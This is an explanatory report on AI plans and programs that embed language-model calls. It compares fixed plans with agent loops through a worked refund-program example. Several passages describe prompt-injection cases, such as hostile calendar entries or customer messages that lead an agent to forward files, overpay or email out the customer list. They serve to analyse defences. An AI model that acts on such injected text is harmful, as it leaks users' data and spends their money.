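# Language-model calls inside AI-generated plans and programs

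## Plans, programs and the model calls inside them

Some AI systems carry out a user's request by having a language model write a *plan*, a program whose steps are all written before any of them runs. Ordinary software then runs the steps. Many plans include an *embedded call*, a step that calls a language model again, for instance to judge whether an email is a complaint. Embedded calls make plans far more useful, since much work requires reading ordinary prose. They also make the system harder to classify, because a model is now making judgements in the middle of a plan that was supposed to be complete before it ran.

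### Models, tools and interpreters

A language model takes in text and returns probabilities for what comes next. Software draws an answer from those probabilities, so the same input can produce different answers. The model carries nothing over from one call to the next except what someone puts into the next input. Its output has no effect by itself, so no money moves when a model writes "pay Ann $40".

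A language model can search the web, read a calendar or issue a payment when the surrounding software connects it to a *tool*, a function that does something beyond producing text. The model writes a request in an agreed format, the software recognises it and runs the tool, and the result comes back to the model as text.

A *program* is a series of instructions in a formal language. It may include loops ("do this for every message") and conditions ("do this only if the answer is yes"). An *interpreter* is software that reads a program and carries out its instructions one at a time, whether or not they are wise. It takes the same steps whenever the program and the values along the way are the same.

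### The agent loop

The usual way to get a language model to do a long task is to let it choose one action at a time. In pseudocode:

```
while not done:
    action = model(goal, history)
    result = execute(action)
    history = history + (action, result)
```

In an *agent loop*, the model sees the goal and everything that has happened so far, picks an action, sees the result and picks again. The standard example is *ReAct* (short for reasoning and acting), which Yao, Zhao and colleagues (2022) set out formally. At step t, the agent has a context cₜ = (o₁, a₁, …, aₜ₋₁, oₜ), the full record of observations o and actions a up to that point, and it draws its next action from a policy π(aₜ | cₜ). Any observation can therefore affect any later action.

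ReAct added thoughts to the actions a model could already take. If A is the set of actions that affect the world and L is the space of language, the model now chooses its next step from A ∪ L. A thought is a piece of text from L that changes nothing in the world and only adds to the context for the next choice. ReAct compares this to a cook who notices halfway through that there is no salt and uses soy sauce instead, a substitution the recipe didn't need to anticipate. Yao and colleagues also found that the model they used sometimes got stuck repeating its earlier thoughts and actions.

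### Writing the whole plan first

The alternative is to have the model plan the work at the start. *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (Del Rosario, Krawiecka and Schroeder de Witt, 2025) describes *plan-then-execute*, in which a planner (usually a strong language model) writes out all the steps and a separate executor carries them out. The executor can be a simple loop that goes through the list and calls the named functions. It can also be a complete ReAct agent that receives one step at a time, in which case only the outline of the work is settled in advance.

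A *fixed plan* is stricter than an outline because its text, including its branches and the actions it permits, does not change once execution begins. In an example from *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025), a user wants today's schedule sent to their boss, John Doe, and the model writes a three-line program. The program reads the calendar, passes the entries to a language model for formatting, and emails the result to John Doe's address. The second line is an embedded call, and the program is already complete when that call runs.

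*SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes a strict version of this arrangement, built for assistants that serve a user over many requests. The planner runs once per request and must produce the whole plan in a small language with six kinds of step: fetch a stored result, call a tool, call a model on some text, show something to the user, branch, and loop. Only the tool step can change anything in the outside world. A deterministic interpreter then runs the plan and cannot add, remove or reorder steps. If a tool fails or a value has the wrong form, SPA stops rather than returning to the planner for a repair.

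A planner that commits to a program early can still make several attempts at it first. Piet, Chow and colleagues (2026), in *Position*, argue for what they call compile-and-execute in agents that use websites. Their proposed compiler, the component that writes the program, may work in a loop, looking up which functions a site offers, drafting code, testing the draft on invented data and revising it. The loop ends before the program handles any live content from the site.

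### Open loop and closed loop

Engineers have older terms for this contrast, *open loop* and *closed loop*. A boiler on a timer runs open loop because it heats for an hour whatever the temperature of the house. A thermostat runs closed loop because it measures the temperature and switches the boiler on or off accordingly. The survey *Agentic Environment Engineering for Large Language Models* (2026) applies these terms to AI agents. An open-loop agent receives one initial observation and executes a predetermined sequence of actions, while a closed-loop agent receives a new observation at each step and adapts.

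Closing the loop lets the model respond when a plan fails. *Using Language Models as Closed-Loop High-Level Planners for Robotics Applications* (2025) lists three causes of failure for robots: the model writes a bad plan, a step in a good plan fails, or the surroundings change while the plan is running. Software has milder versions of these problems. Piet and colleagues describe a search for "COVID location tracker" that finds nothing because the project's description lacks the word "tracker". A ReAct agent would respond to the empty result with a broader search, but a compiled program fails unless its author wrote code to handle empty results.

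*AdaPlanner* (Sun, Zhuang and colleagues, 2023) further divides closed-loop systems by what the feedback changes. In an implicit closed loop, the agent adjusts its next action but leaves the plan P₀ unchanged. In an explicit one, it rewrites the entire remaining plan, so each plan Pₜ depends on the previous plan and everything observed since. *AdaPlanner* lists ReAct among the methods "with fixed plan", whereas *Self-Improvement of Large Language Models* (2026), a technical overview, presents ReAct as a departure from fixed plans. They seem to disagree mostly about what "fixed plan" means. A ReAct agent may well keep the same overall intention throughout, but no text written in advance limits what it can do next, so strictly speaking it has no fixed plan.

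A fixed plan need not be open loop. A thermostat follows one unchanging rule, yet it is the textbook example of feedback. Similarly, a program with a condition in it acts on a value that did not exist at planning time, without any change to its text. The survey's definition of open loop fits a bare list of actions but not a program with branches, and most useful programs have branches.

### Control flow, data flow and prompt injection

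The terms *control flow* and *data flow* help describe what a fixed plan fixes. Control flow is which steps run, in what order and under what conditions. Data flow is how values pass from one step to another. In the calendar program, the control flow is to read the calendar, format the entries and then send the email. In its data flow, the calendar entries pass through the formatting model into the body of the email, while the address comes from the user's request.

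Much of the interest in the difference comes from *prompt injection*, in which a model follows text in the data it reads as if that text were an instruction. For example, an attacker might send a calendar invitation that includes an instruction to forward the user's files to a stranger. Girrens and Wang trace the problem to instructions and data sharing the same natural-language channel. The model receives both as a single stretch of text, with nothing to mark which sentences have authority.

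Prompt injection is about as bad as it could be in the agent loop, because the hostile text arrives just when the model is choosing what to do. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) describes the damage formally by comparing two agents with the same plan. The reference agent executes the plan step by step. The language-model agent can, at any point, either take the next step or make a call that the attacker injected, which leaves its place in the plan unchanged. In this formalization, an injection is an extra action inserted between the plan's steps, and an interpreter restricted to those steps cannot take it.

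An attacker can still manipulate the data that flows through a plan. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out that a hostile calendar entry cannot add a second email but can change the contents of the email to John Doe arbitrarily. An attacker doesn't always need an instruction, either. In an example from Girrens and Wang, an assistant pays an invoice exactly as the user asked, but the account number on the invoice belongs to the attacker.

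Data can also mislead a model that doesn't mistake it for a command. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) calls this judgment manipulation. An agent has to read data to make decisions, so whoever writes the data can try to influence them. Piet and colleagues make a similar distinction between control-flow hijacking, where the attacker gets the agent to take actions outside its task, and outcome manipulation, where the task stays the same but its result changes. They compare the first to running arbitrary code in ordinary software, and the second to tampering with a program's variables.

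People want fixed plans partly for security, because untrusted text that arrives after planning cannot add an action to the plan. They also want a person or a checking program to be able to review every action the plan permits before any of them happens. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues worry that tired users will approve unsafe actions, so they would have reason to prefer this review to confirmation at each step. Another reason is cost. An agent loop calls a model at every action, whereas the expensive planner in plan-then-execute may run only once, with cheaper models or plain code doing the rest, as Del Rosario and colleagues note.

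### The refund program

Consider a shop owner with 50 unread customer messages. She tells her assistant to refund every customer whose message reports a broken item, up to $50 each. The planning model has not seen the messages. It knows the request and the available tools, and it writes this:

```
for message in inbox.read(50):
    answer = model("Is a broken item reported, yes or no?", message.text)
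    if answer == "yes":
        refund(message.customer, min(message.order_price, 50))
```

The interpreter goes through the messages in order, sending the question and the text of each message to a language model. If the model returns "yes", the interpreter calls the refund tool with the price of the order or $50, whichever is lower. A keyword search would do this job poorly, because some customers write that the mug "arrived in two pieces" or that the lamp "won't turn on", while others write that their *old* lamp broke and they love the new one.

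Several papers describe similar programs. In an early example, Sun and colleagues let a model-written program use an `ask_LLM()` action to extract, say, the name of an object from a description of a room. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a search for invoices in which a separate model call on each file returns true or false, so a malicious file can at most get itself counted as an invoice. Piet and colleagues examined web tasks including "Delete negative reviews", where a model's classification of each review determines whether it is deleted.

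An agent loop working through the same inbox would read message 17 with access to the refund tool and any other tools it had, and with messages 1 to 16 still in its history. A line in message 17 could lead it to refund $500, refund somebody else, or email the customer list to an outsider. In the refund program, the model that reads message 17 can only reply yes or no, and its reply doesn't affect the question about message 18, which goes to the model with no history. The worst case is 50 refunds of $50, or $2,500, all to people who wrote to the owner, and she can work this out before she runs the program.

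Within that worst case, the program still allows 2⁵⁰ different outcomes, roughly a quadrillion, because each of the 50 messages may or may not lead to a refund. The shop owner approved all of these outcomes when she approved the program's text. Which one happens depends on how a language model answers after reading messages from strangers. A customer whose item is fine can try to get a refund by lying, which might also fool a human clerk, or by adding a line that tells the model to answer yes, which would not fool a clerk.

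The program easily meets the definition of a fixed plan, since nobody writes a new step after it starts. Yet a model makes 50 decisions while it runs, each based on something the planner never saw and each with money at stake. The definition doesn't specify how much the branches may leave open, and here they leave open every payment. Instead of a yes or no, the embedded call could also return a sum of money, the name of a tool, or even a block of new code for the interpreter to run, while the four lines around it stayed almost the same.

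## Three kinds of embedded call: function, sub-agent and planner

The embedded call in the refund program returns yes or no, and the program handles everything else. Other embedded calls look up information before returning a result, or write new steps for the interpreter to carry out. These kinds of call differ in what they read, what they can do while they run, and whether the program stores their output as a value or executes it.

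A *language-model function* has no tools. It takes in data and returns a value, which the program stores in a variable. A *sub-agent* has its own tools and chooses which steps to take with them before it returns. A *planner re-invocation* calls the planning model again for new steps, which the interpreter then executes.

Piet and colleagues allow only language-model functions in their proposed web programs. They describe the opposite extreme as a program that calls arbitrary sub-agents and executes their outputs, which would bring back the agent loop. Those sub-agents can both use tools and write instructions for the interpreter, but a call can have one of these abilities without the other. A planner needs no tools, but the interpreter turns the text it writes into actions, so taking away a call's tools is not enough to make it harmless.

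Any of the three kinds of call might take a stranger's email as input, or only the user's own words. The input determines who can influence the result, but not which kind of call it is.

### The refund program, three ways

The refund program as it stands uses a language-model function. The call reads one message and can do nothing except answer, and the program only compares the answer with "yes". Here is the same job with a sub-agent:

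```
for message in inbox.read(50):
    outcome = agent("Refund this customer, up to $50, if an item arrived broken.",
                    message, tools=[find_order, track_parcel, refund])
    log(outcome)
```

The sub-agent can do better work because it can look things up, such as the earlier order when a customer writes "same problem as last time". But it now has the refund tool, and the $50 limit is an English instruction that the model might not follow instead of a check in the code. The program still goes through 50 messages and its text never changes, but you can no longer tell from the text who gets paid, how much or how often, and in the worst case the sub-agent could issue any refunds the tool permits.

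The owner can restore the old limit by changing the tools. She could supply a refund tool that works once per message, only for the customer who sent it, and only up to $50, which makes the worst case $2,500 again. Or she could let the sub-agent keep only its two look-up tools and return yes or no, and have the program issue the refund. A hostile message might then get the sub-agent to look up other people's orders, but the limit on payments would hold.

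With a planner re-invocation, the program looks like this:

```
for message in inbox.read(50):
    steps = planner("Write the steps that deal with this message.",
                    request, message.text)
    run(steps)
```

The planner can respond in a way nobody foresaw, such as sending a replacement lamp and asking for the broken one back. A misleading message can also cause it to write any step the interpreter supports, including one that emails the customer list to an outsider. Someone who reads this program before it runs learns almost nothing about what will happen and would have to review up to 50 further programs to find out.

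A planner is much safer if it never reads the messages. *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (Chow, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) describes Baya, a web agent that works this way. Baya turns a request into a Python program before it interacts with the live site. If the program fails, the planner receives the old code and a restricted error report, but no content from the website, and writes a corrected version. Chow and colleagues found these repairs necessary because websites have rules that their documentation omits. For example, one shopping site's documentation describes product options as optional, but the site rejects clothing without a size and colour.

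Baya's plan isn't strictly fixed, because its text can change after execution begins. SPA, the strict system from the previous section, would stop instead. Still, a hostile product review can't determine the new steps, because the planner never receives it, and the corrected program can use only operations the researchers prepared for the site in advance.

### Model calls in early plans

Researchers were putting model calls inside model-written programs by 2022. Cheng, Xie and colleagues (2022), in *Binding Language Models in Symbolic Languages*, wanted to answer questions about tables with SQL, the standard language for querying databases. SQL can sort and filter, but it can't tell from a column of country names which countries are in North America. Their system, Binder, lets the model write a query with calls to a model inside it. For "which is the best-selling shirt made in North America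 and with no chemicals?", the query has roughly this form:

```
SELECT shirt FROM products
WHERE f_col("North America?"; made_in) = 'yes'
  AND f_col("No chemicals?"; shirt) = 'yes'
ORDER BY sales DESC LIMIT 1
```

The language-model function `f_col` sends a question and a column to the model and gets back a new column of answers, which SQL then treats like any other. A second language-model function, `f_val`, returns a single value, for questions such as which shirt is the most formal. A call could take another call's result as its input. The same model, OpenAI's Codex, wrote the query and answered the calls. It was given the column names and the first three rows of the table before writing the query, so unlike the planner in the refund program, it had seen some of the data.

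On a standard set of table questions, Binder got 64.6% right, against 61.1% for the same model writing plain SQL and 48.7% for the model answering directly. Binder did hardly better than the model answering directly on questions that plain SQL can't express (41.3% against 40.3%), but far better on the rest (71.8% against 53.4%). The embedded calls let programs cover more questions, though most of the advantage over asking the model directly came from the ordinary SQL around them. A query can also consist of one call that passes the whole question and the whole table to the model, as Cheng and colleagues point out, in which case the program contributes nothing.

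Xu, Peng and colleagues (2023), in *ReWOO*, made the model one tool among several. A planner writes the complete list of steps, with placeholders such as #E1 for results that don't exist yet. Workers then carry out the steps and fill in the placeholders, and a final model call, the solver, reads everything and answers. For the question whether this year's Speaker of the House is older than last year's, a plan might be:

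```
#E1 = SearchDoc[Speaker of the House 2023]
#E2 = Google[Speaker of the House 2022]
#E3 = LLM[Who is older? Use #E1 and #E2]
```

The `LLM` step is a language-model function that happens to sit in the same menu as a search engine and a calculator.

Xu and colleagues were mainly after lower cost. An agent loop resends its instructions and its entire history at every step. Suppose the fixed part of the prompt takes c tokens (the word fragments by which providers charge) and each step adds h more. Over k steps, a simplified version of their calculation gives these totals for the input:

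- agent loop: kc + hk(k − 1)/2
- ReWOO: 2c + hk

With ten steps, c = 1,000 and h = 200, the loop reads 19,000 tokens and ReWOO reads 4,000. On HotpotQA, a set of questions that require facts from more than one Wikipedia article, ReWOO used 1,986 tokens per question against 9,795 for ReAct, and was right slightly more often (42.4% against 40.8%). The accuracy results are weaker evidence for ReWOO than the token savings, because on a set of trivia questions the same model with no tools scored 80.6%, against 66.6% for ReWOO and 59.4% for ReAct.

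*AdaPlanner* (Sun et al.) combined two of these kinds of call. Its in-plan refinement keeps the existing program and uses a language-model function, the `ask_LLM()` action from the previous section. Its out-of-plan refinement calls the planner again to rewrite the plan.

In *Code as Policies*, Liang, Huang and colleagues (2022) make the extra model calls before the program runs. Their model writes Python for a robot and may use functions that don't exist yet. Told to stack the blocks in the empty bowl, it might write a call to `stack_objs_in_order` without having defined it. Software then finds the undefined functions and has the model write each one, repeating the process if the new functions depend on others that are undefined. The model calls are nested, but the finished program can be a fixed plan with no model calls in it.

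The complete system also uses a second mechanism. *LMPVC and Policy Bank* (2025), a paper that adapts the method to industrial robots, distinguishes this hierarchical generation from composition, in which one model-written program calls another. In an example from Liang and colleagues, the robot must keep moving the leftmost block to the right while that block is the red one. Its program calls `parse_obj('the left most block')` inside the loop. Each time, this embedded call makes the model output a few lines of code that compare the blocks' positions, and Python runs them to get the name of a block. The survey *Code as Agent Harness* (2026) treats *Code as Policies* as the template for a line of robot systems, some of which now generate and run code in a continuing loop.

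### DSPy

DSPy, a Python framework for writing programs that call language models, makes the differences between the kinds easy to see. Khattab, Singhvi and colleagues (2023) designed it to replace the long hand-written prompts that such programs usually contained. A developer instead writes a *signature*, a short declaration of the inputs and outputs. `"question -> answer"` is a complete signature, and DSPy builds a prompt from the field names.

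A *module* is a way of carrying out a signature. The simplest, `Predict`, makes one model call and reads the output fields from the reply. `ChainOfThought` adds a field for reasoning, which the model must fill in before it answers. Developers combine modules in ordinary Python, with any loops and conditions they like. The refund program would look like this:

```
class Refunds(dspy.Module):
    def __init__(self):
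        self.judge = dspy.Predict("message -> broken_item: bool")

    def forward(self, messages):
        for m in messages:
            if self.judge(message=m.text).broken_item:
                refund(m.customer, min(m.order_price, 50))
```

An *optimizer* then tunes the prompts. It takes the program, some training examples and a *metric*, a function that scores the program's output. The basic version runs the program on the examples, keeps the runs that pass the metric, and adds the inputs and outputs of each step in those runs to the prompts as worked examples. The developer usually supplies only the final answers, because a successful run provides the intermediate ones. Other versions search through many sets of worked examples, retrain the model, or run several tuned copies of the program and take a majority vote. A newer optimizer, DSPy's GEPA, uses a model to analyze records of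 the program's runs and propose better instructions.

In 2023, two rounds of tuning raised the accuracy of GPT-3.5 with a bare `"question -> answer"` from 24.0% to 64.7% on school maths problems. Khattab and colleagues inspected the tuned prompts and found that the model could now write out its reasoning in the answer field before giving the number. The metric allowed this because it checked only the final number. Tuning had in effect turned the call into `ChainOfThought`. The tuned call was still a language-model function because it had gained no tools and the program still stored its answer as a value.

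Changing one line of the refund program would change the kind of call:

```
self.judge = dspy.ReAct("message -> broken_item: bool",
                        tools=[find_order, track_parcel])
```

`ReAct` runs an agent loop and then returns the same true-or-false field, so the rest of the program works as before. Because the signature is identical, a reviewer who checked only the signatures would miss that a function had become a sub-agent. The amount of work also becomes less predictable. When DSPy's developers tested a program that writes haiku, the model made as many as eight tool calls in some runs and skipped its research in others.

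Khattab and colleagues also compared the two kinds on HotPotQA. One program ran a loop exactly twice, using a language-model function to write a search query each time, and then used another function to write the answer. The other program was a `ReAct` module that chose its own searches, up to a limit of five rounds. With GPT-3.5 and tuned prompts, the fixed loop got 48.7% right and `ReAct` got 39.0%. The fixed loop had an advantage because it retrieved three passages per search and `ReAct` only one, and a current model might well do better with `ReAct`. Still, the result shows that two rounds of a fixed loop can be enough for a task that seems to need an agent.

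DSPy has since acquired more modules, which DSPy's *Built-in module variants* describes. Sorted by kind, as they appear to the program that calls them, they come out like this:

| Module | What it does | Kind of call |
|---|---|---|
| `Predict`, `ChainOfThought` | Makes one model call and returns the output fields | Language-model function |
| `BestOfN`, `Refine` | Runs another module several times and keeps the best-scoring result | Same as the module it runs |
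| `ProgramOfThought` | Has the model write Python, runs it, and extracts an answer from the result | Sub-agent with an interpreter as its only tool |
| `ReAct` | Has the model choose tools in a loop until it finishes | Sub-agent |
| `CodeAct` | Has the model write Python that calls tools, also in a loop | Sub-agent |
| `RLM` (experimental) | Has the model write Python that can call a model again | Sub-agent |

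`RLM` stands for recursive language model, a design covered in a later section. According to DSPy's *ReAct and ReActV2*, a new implementation will take over the name `ReAct` in version 3.5. It lets the model request several tools in one turn and keeps earlier turns unchanged in the prompt, so that a provider can reuse its work on them. DSPy's developers have seen savings of up to 50% on some tasks in internal tests, which would reduce ReWOO's cost advantage over an agent loop.

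### Programs by people and programs by models

Most DSPy programs aren't plans as this report uses the word, because a person writes them. But the embedded calls work the same way, and a customer's message has the same influence over `if broken_item: refund(...)` whether a person or a model wrote the line. A developer's program gets more attention, because the developer writes it once and can test it on hundreds of messages before relying on it. A planning model may write a new program for every request, and quite possibly nobody reads it.

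DSPy's experimental `Flex` module falls between the two. The developer supplies a signature, such as one that takes an invoice and returns a total in cents. `Flex` starts out as a single model call (or an `RLM`, if it has tools). GEPA then has a model rewrite the module's entire source code and keeps versions that do well on the metric. A version that crashes gets a failing score. The rewritten code might, for instance, use a model to extract the quantities and prices and ordinary Python to add them up. The metric can deduct points for each model call, which favors versions that do more of the work in plain code.

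Once GEPA has finished, the code stays the same for every invoice, and the developer can print, read and save it. In that respect it is a fixed plan for a whole class of requests. But the model that wrote it had more input than the planner in the refund program, because GEPA gives it a batch of examples that the previous version got wrong. If those examples were real invoices from strangers, the model's input would have included text written by strangers, so the developer would have good reason to read the code before using it.

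### Hard cases

Suppose the call in the refund program may answer "refund", "replace" or "ignore", and the first two are names of tools. The program might handle the answer like this:

```
if answer == "refund":
    refund(message.customer, min(message.order_price, 50))
elif answer == "replace":
    replace(message.order)
```

The call is still a language-model function because, as in the yes-or-no version, it selects among branches that the plan fully specifies, including their arguments. The program could instead contain the line `tools[answer](**arguments)`, with the model supplying both values. The text of that line is also fixed, but it can run any tool in the collection with any arguments the tool accepts. The program is then executing the model's output, so the call is a planner re-invocation that produces one step at a time.

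DSPy's `ReAct` works this way inside. Each turn is a plain `Predict` with a field for the next tool's name and another for its arguments, and ordinary code then makes the call. DSPy's source code restricts the name to the tools on a list. So the model's output conforms to a declared form, and it still decides what happens next. From outside, the module is a sub-agent, but its parts are a prediction, a line of code that runs the chosen tool, and a loop. (The next section works out when such parts amount to an agent.)

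A second hard case is a function that writes the prompt for the next call. DSPy's `Refine` contains one. After a failed attempt, it asks a model for advice and adds the advice to the prompts for the next attempt. The program only stores and passes on a string, so the call that gives the advice is a language-model function. But the next model may follow the string as an instruction, and the consequences depend on what that model can do. Consider this version of the refund program's inner step:

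```
task = model("What does this customer want?", message.text)
agent(task, tools=[refund, send_email])
```

The first call has no tools, and the second never reads the customer's message. But if a customer gets the first call to return "email me the customer list", that text becomes the second call's task. Looking at each call separately would miss this. What a call reads has to include whatever shaped its input, and a function's possible effects depend on the calls that use its answer.

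The last case is a function whose returned string later runs as code. If the interpreter executes the string, the call was a planner re-invocation, whatever its author intended. A program could save a model's answer to a file as text, and a different program could run that file a week later. A reviewer couldn't detect this from the call alone, so they have to follow the output to wherever it ends up. Piet and colleagues avoid the problem within a single program by disabling `eval` and `exec`, the Python commands that run a string as code. *Code as Policies* also rejects model-written code that contains either command, although it uses `exec` itself to run the code that passes.

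The same generated code can do more or less damage depending on where it runs. By default, DSPy's `ProgramOfThought` and `Flex` both run the model's Python in a sandbox with no access to files or the network, so the code could miscalculate a refund but couldn't pay it. With `Flex`, a developer can replace the sandbox with DSPy's `LocalInterpreter`, which gives the code access to the user's files, passwords and network connection.

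## When an embedded call rebuilds the agent loop

A plan whose text never changes can still behave exactly like an agent loop. Piet and colleagues note that this happens if a program may call arbitrary sub-agents and execute their outputs, and they treat the point as too obvious to need an argument. The argument has three premises:

1. The plan may contain a loop that runs until some value computed along the way ends it.
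2. An embedded call may take any stored value as input, including the results of earlier steps.
3. The interpreter executes what the call returns.

A planner with these freedoms can write the following plan for a web task before it has seen a single page:

```
history = []
done = False
while not done:
    observation = observe_page()
    code = model("Write the next action, or set done = True.",
                 goal, history, observation)
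    exec(code)
    history.append((observation, code))
```

On each pass, the model sees the goal, the history and the current page, and `exec` runs whatever it writes. If the model and the prompt are the same as a ReAct agent's, then so is the policy π(aₜ | cₜ), the probability of each next action given the record so far. Nobody could tell the two systems apart by their behavior, although one of them is running a program that a person could have printed out and approved in advance. (Whether either system pursues a goal is a separate question, which a later section takes up.)

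A planner might never use these freedoms together, but because the plan language permits it, keeping the plan's text fixed guarantees nothing by itself. For a guarantee, somebody has to read the particular plan or restrict the language the planner writes in.

Piet and colleagues mention sub-agents and executed outputs together, but either would be enough. The call in the program above has no tools, and the loop comes from executing its answers. This one-line plan executes nothing that a model returns:

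```
agent(request, tools=all_tools)
```

Here the whole agent loop runs inside the call. A longer plan has the same gap if an agent carries out its steps. Piet and colleagues object that a hostile page can still influence what that agent does at each step.

### A loop without generated code

Banning `exec` removes the third premise, but the loop can survive the ban. Suppose the shop owner's planner wrote this program:

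```
history = []
for turn in range(20):
    choice = model("Choose the next tool and its arguments.", request, history)
    match choice.tool:
        case "read_inbox":  result = read_inbox(**choice.args)
        case "find_order":  result = find_order(**choice.args)
        case "refund":      result = refund(**choice.args)
        case "send_email":  result = send_email(**choice.args)
        # ... six more tools ...
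        case "finish":      break
    history.append((choice, result))
```

The `match` statement compares the model's choice with a list of names and runs the matching line. Nothing the model writes runs as code, but the model can still do anything in 20 turns that a ReAct agent with the same ten tools could do. In the previous section, a call that named a tool and supplied its arguments counted as a planner re-invocation producing one step at a time. It still counts as one when the ten cases are written out in the program.

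The `ReAct` module in DSPy, which the previous section examined, is essentially this program, with a default limit of 20 turns. DSPy's guide to the module, *Tools, ReAct, and MCP*, explains that "finish" is itself a tool on the list, so the model ends the loop by choosing it as it would any other tool. If a tool fails, the error message goes into the record and the model can try something else.

The switch program would pass the checks that Piet and colleagues propose for their interpreter. It never uses `eval` or `exec`, each answer can conform to a declared schema, and every tool call is already in the program's text. But it breaks their rule that no language model decides which call runs next. The interpreter's checks don't enforce this rule, so someone has to examine the program for violations. Piet and colleagues list static checking of generated programs as an open problem.

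Their main security property also holds for the switch program, since hostile content can't add an instruction or a tool. But the property gives little protection when the program can already call all ten tools with any arguments. An attacker who gets the model to email out the customer list has only made the program follow a path it already contained. This counts as outcome manipulation, although it harms the shop owner as much as a hijacking would.

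Narrower output schemas don't necessarily help. Four yes/no answers are enough to pick one of up to 16 tools, and seven more can specify one character of an email. No sensible planner would compose an email this way, but a checker that only confirmed that every call returned yes or no would approve a plan that did.

### Four conditions

The `exec` program and the switch program have four properties in common, which together rebuild the agent loop:

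- *Feedback*: the call sees the results of earlier actions, including actions that earlier calls selected.
- *Selection*: the call's output determines which action comes next.
- *Repetition*: the call sits in a loop or a recursion without a small bound.
- *Range*: the actions and arguments open to selection are wide.

The refund program makes 50 calls, so it has repetition. It also has a limited form of selection, because each answer determines whether the program issues a refund. It has almost no range, and it lacks the relevant kind of feedback, because no call's input includes earlier answers or their results.

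Hugging Face's *What are agents?*, a guide to the company's agent library, grades programs similarly, but by individual constructs. A program earns one star if the model's output controls an if/else branch, two if it chooses a function to run or decides whether a loop continues, and three if it starts other agents or writes code. This gives the switch program two stars and the `exec` program three, although both satisfy all four conditions. The higher rating does reflect a real difference, since generated code can combine tools in ways that a switch can't.

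#### Removing feedback

Without feedback, the model chooses tools but never receives their output. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues call this design an action selector. Their example is a customer-service chatbot that can fetch a link to the customer's last order or direct the customer to the password or payment settings. Hostile text in the order can't affect the chatbot because it never reads the order, but the customer's own message still can.

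If the switch program recorded the model's choices but not the results, the model would be writing an open-loop plan one line at a time. The software could just as well collect all 20 choices before running the first. Any sequence of tools would still be possible, but strangers' messages couldn't influence which one ran. The program also couldn't do the owner's task, which requires refunding people based on what they wrote.

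An error message is also feedback, and part of its text may come from a website or a stranger. Piet and colleagues suggest that after a failure the planner could write a new program using only a typed error code and the user's clarification. A code from a list of eight carries at most three bits, so an attacker who controlled it could select one of eight new prompts but couldn't write the prompt's text.

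#### Removing selection

A call can read everything, repeatedly, and still have no say in what happens next:

```
summary = ""
for message in inbox.read(50):
    summary = model("Update the summary.", summary, message.text)
send_email(owner, summary)
```

Each call receives the summary that the earlier calls produced, so a hostile message can corrupt the summary from that point on. But the message can't change the program's actions, which are always 50 calls and one email to the owner. Plan-then-execute has the same trade-off.

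The model can regain its choice of actions through an argument passed to a tool. If the last line were `run_shell(summary)`, where `run_shell` passes text to the computer's command line, the program would have the same structure, but the model could run almost any command by writing it into `summary`. A reviewer who checked only which tools the plan names, and in what order, would see one harmless-looking step.

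#### Removing repetition

With a single turn, the switch program makes one choice from ten tools. One bad choice can be expensive if it issues a $5,000 refund, for example, but many attacks need several steps. To email the customer list to an outsider, the model has to read the hostile message, look up the list and send it. That takes three turns, so a limit of two would prevent it. How low the limit has to be therefore depends on the tools.

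A reviewer who searches only for `while` and `for` will miss other forms of repetition, such as recursion or the same step pasted twenty times in a row. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes a small programming language for agents in which the interpreter can parse a model's reply as code and evaluate it. The paper includes a retry loop written as a function that calls itself. If the model's code contains a syntax error, the function sends the error message back and tries again, for up to five rounds. In the example, the model needed three rounds to write a correctly formed factorial function.

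The loop can also come from outside the program. A scheduler that reruns a one-turn program every hour creates one, as long as each run can read something the previous run produced, such as a sent email or a saved file.

#### Narrowing the range

Suppose the model can see every message and every earlier refund, and can take any number of turns, but can only approve one refund of up to $50 per customer. With 50 customers, it can refund at most $2,500. This is an agent loop by definition, since the model observes, acts, sees the result and acts again, but it poses little danger because the possible loss is capped.

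The number of tools is a poor guide to how much an agent can do. Browser agents often have only a few actions, such as click, type and scroll, but Piet and colleagues point out that the effect of a click depends on the page. Clicking the same spot on the screen might open a product page, place an order or delete something. Those few actions can do more than ten tools that each read a different section of an online shop's catalog.

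Piet and colleagues also let the system return to ReAct when a compiled program fails, provided the user agrees and the agent has fewer privileges. For example, the agent might get only functions that read data, or need the user's confirmation for each change. Such an agent still has the first three properties in full, because the restrictions limit only its range.

### Scripts that start agents

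Dynamic workflows, a feature of Anthropic's coding assistant Claude Code, combine these conditions. The model writes a JavaScript program, and the runtime that executes it can start hundreds of sub-agents. According to the feature's documentation, *Orchestrate subagents at scale with dynamic workflows*, the script determines what runs next in a workflow, whereas Claude decides turn by turn when it uses ordinary sub-agents.

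A sample script in the documentation looks for missing security checks in a codebase. Slightly shortened, it reads:

```
const found = await agent('List every .ts file under src/routes/.',
                          {schema: ...})
const audits = await pipeline(found.files, file =>
    agent(`Audit ${file} for missing authentication checks.`))
return audits.filter(Boolean)
```

The first sub-agent returns a list of file names, and the script starts one auditor sub-agent for each name. The list therefore determines the number of auditors and supplies part of each one's instructions. The script fixes everything else about which agents start and when. But each auditor has tools and chooses its own actions, so the table's answer is correct for the script's steps but not for the auditors' actions within them.

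Another suggested workflow runs a type checker and keeps fixing the reported errors until the check passes or two rounds in a row make no progress. This workflow also meets all four conditions at the level of the script. The agents in each round see the errors left by the last round, they decide what to edit, the number of rounds has no fixed limit, and an edit can be any code. The script's text is fixed, like the refund program's.

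Anthropic's *A harness for every task* (2026) calls this pattern "loop until done" and says users can cap a workflow at, for example, 10,000 tokens. A token cap limits cost better than it limits harm, since a command that deletes a folder takes only a few tokens. Claude Code's permission rules are more useful for limiting harm because they still apply to the sub-agents' tool calls and so restrict what the sub-agents can do.

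### Counting paths

A fixed plan and an agent also differ in how many ways they can run. A plan with three yes/no calls has at most 2³ = 8 paths, and a reviewer could read all of them. The switch program has 10²⁰ possible tool sequences if it uses all 20 turns, or about 1.1 × 10²⁰ including runs that finish early. Checking them all at a billion per second would take more than 3,000 years.

The owner can review the refund program in a minute, although its 2⁵⁰ outcomes make it look bad by this measure too. A computer could check them all in 13 days at the same speed, but no person could. The owner only has to consider the outcome in which all 50 refunds are paid, because every other outcome is that one with some refunds left out.

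No single outcome of the switch program includes all the others. What `send_email` can reveal depends on what the model has already read, and a refund to the wrong person is a separate outcome from a refund to the right one.

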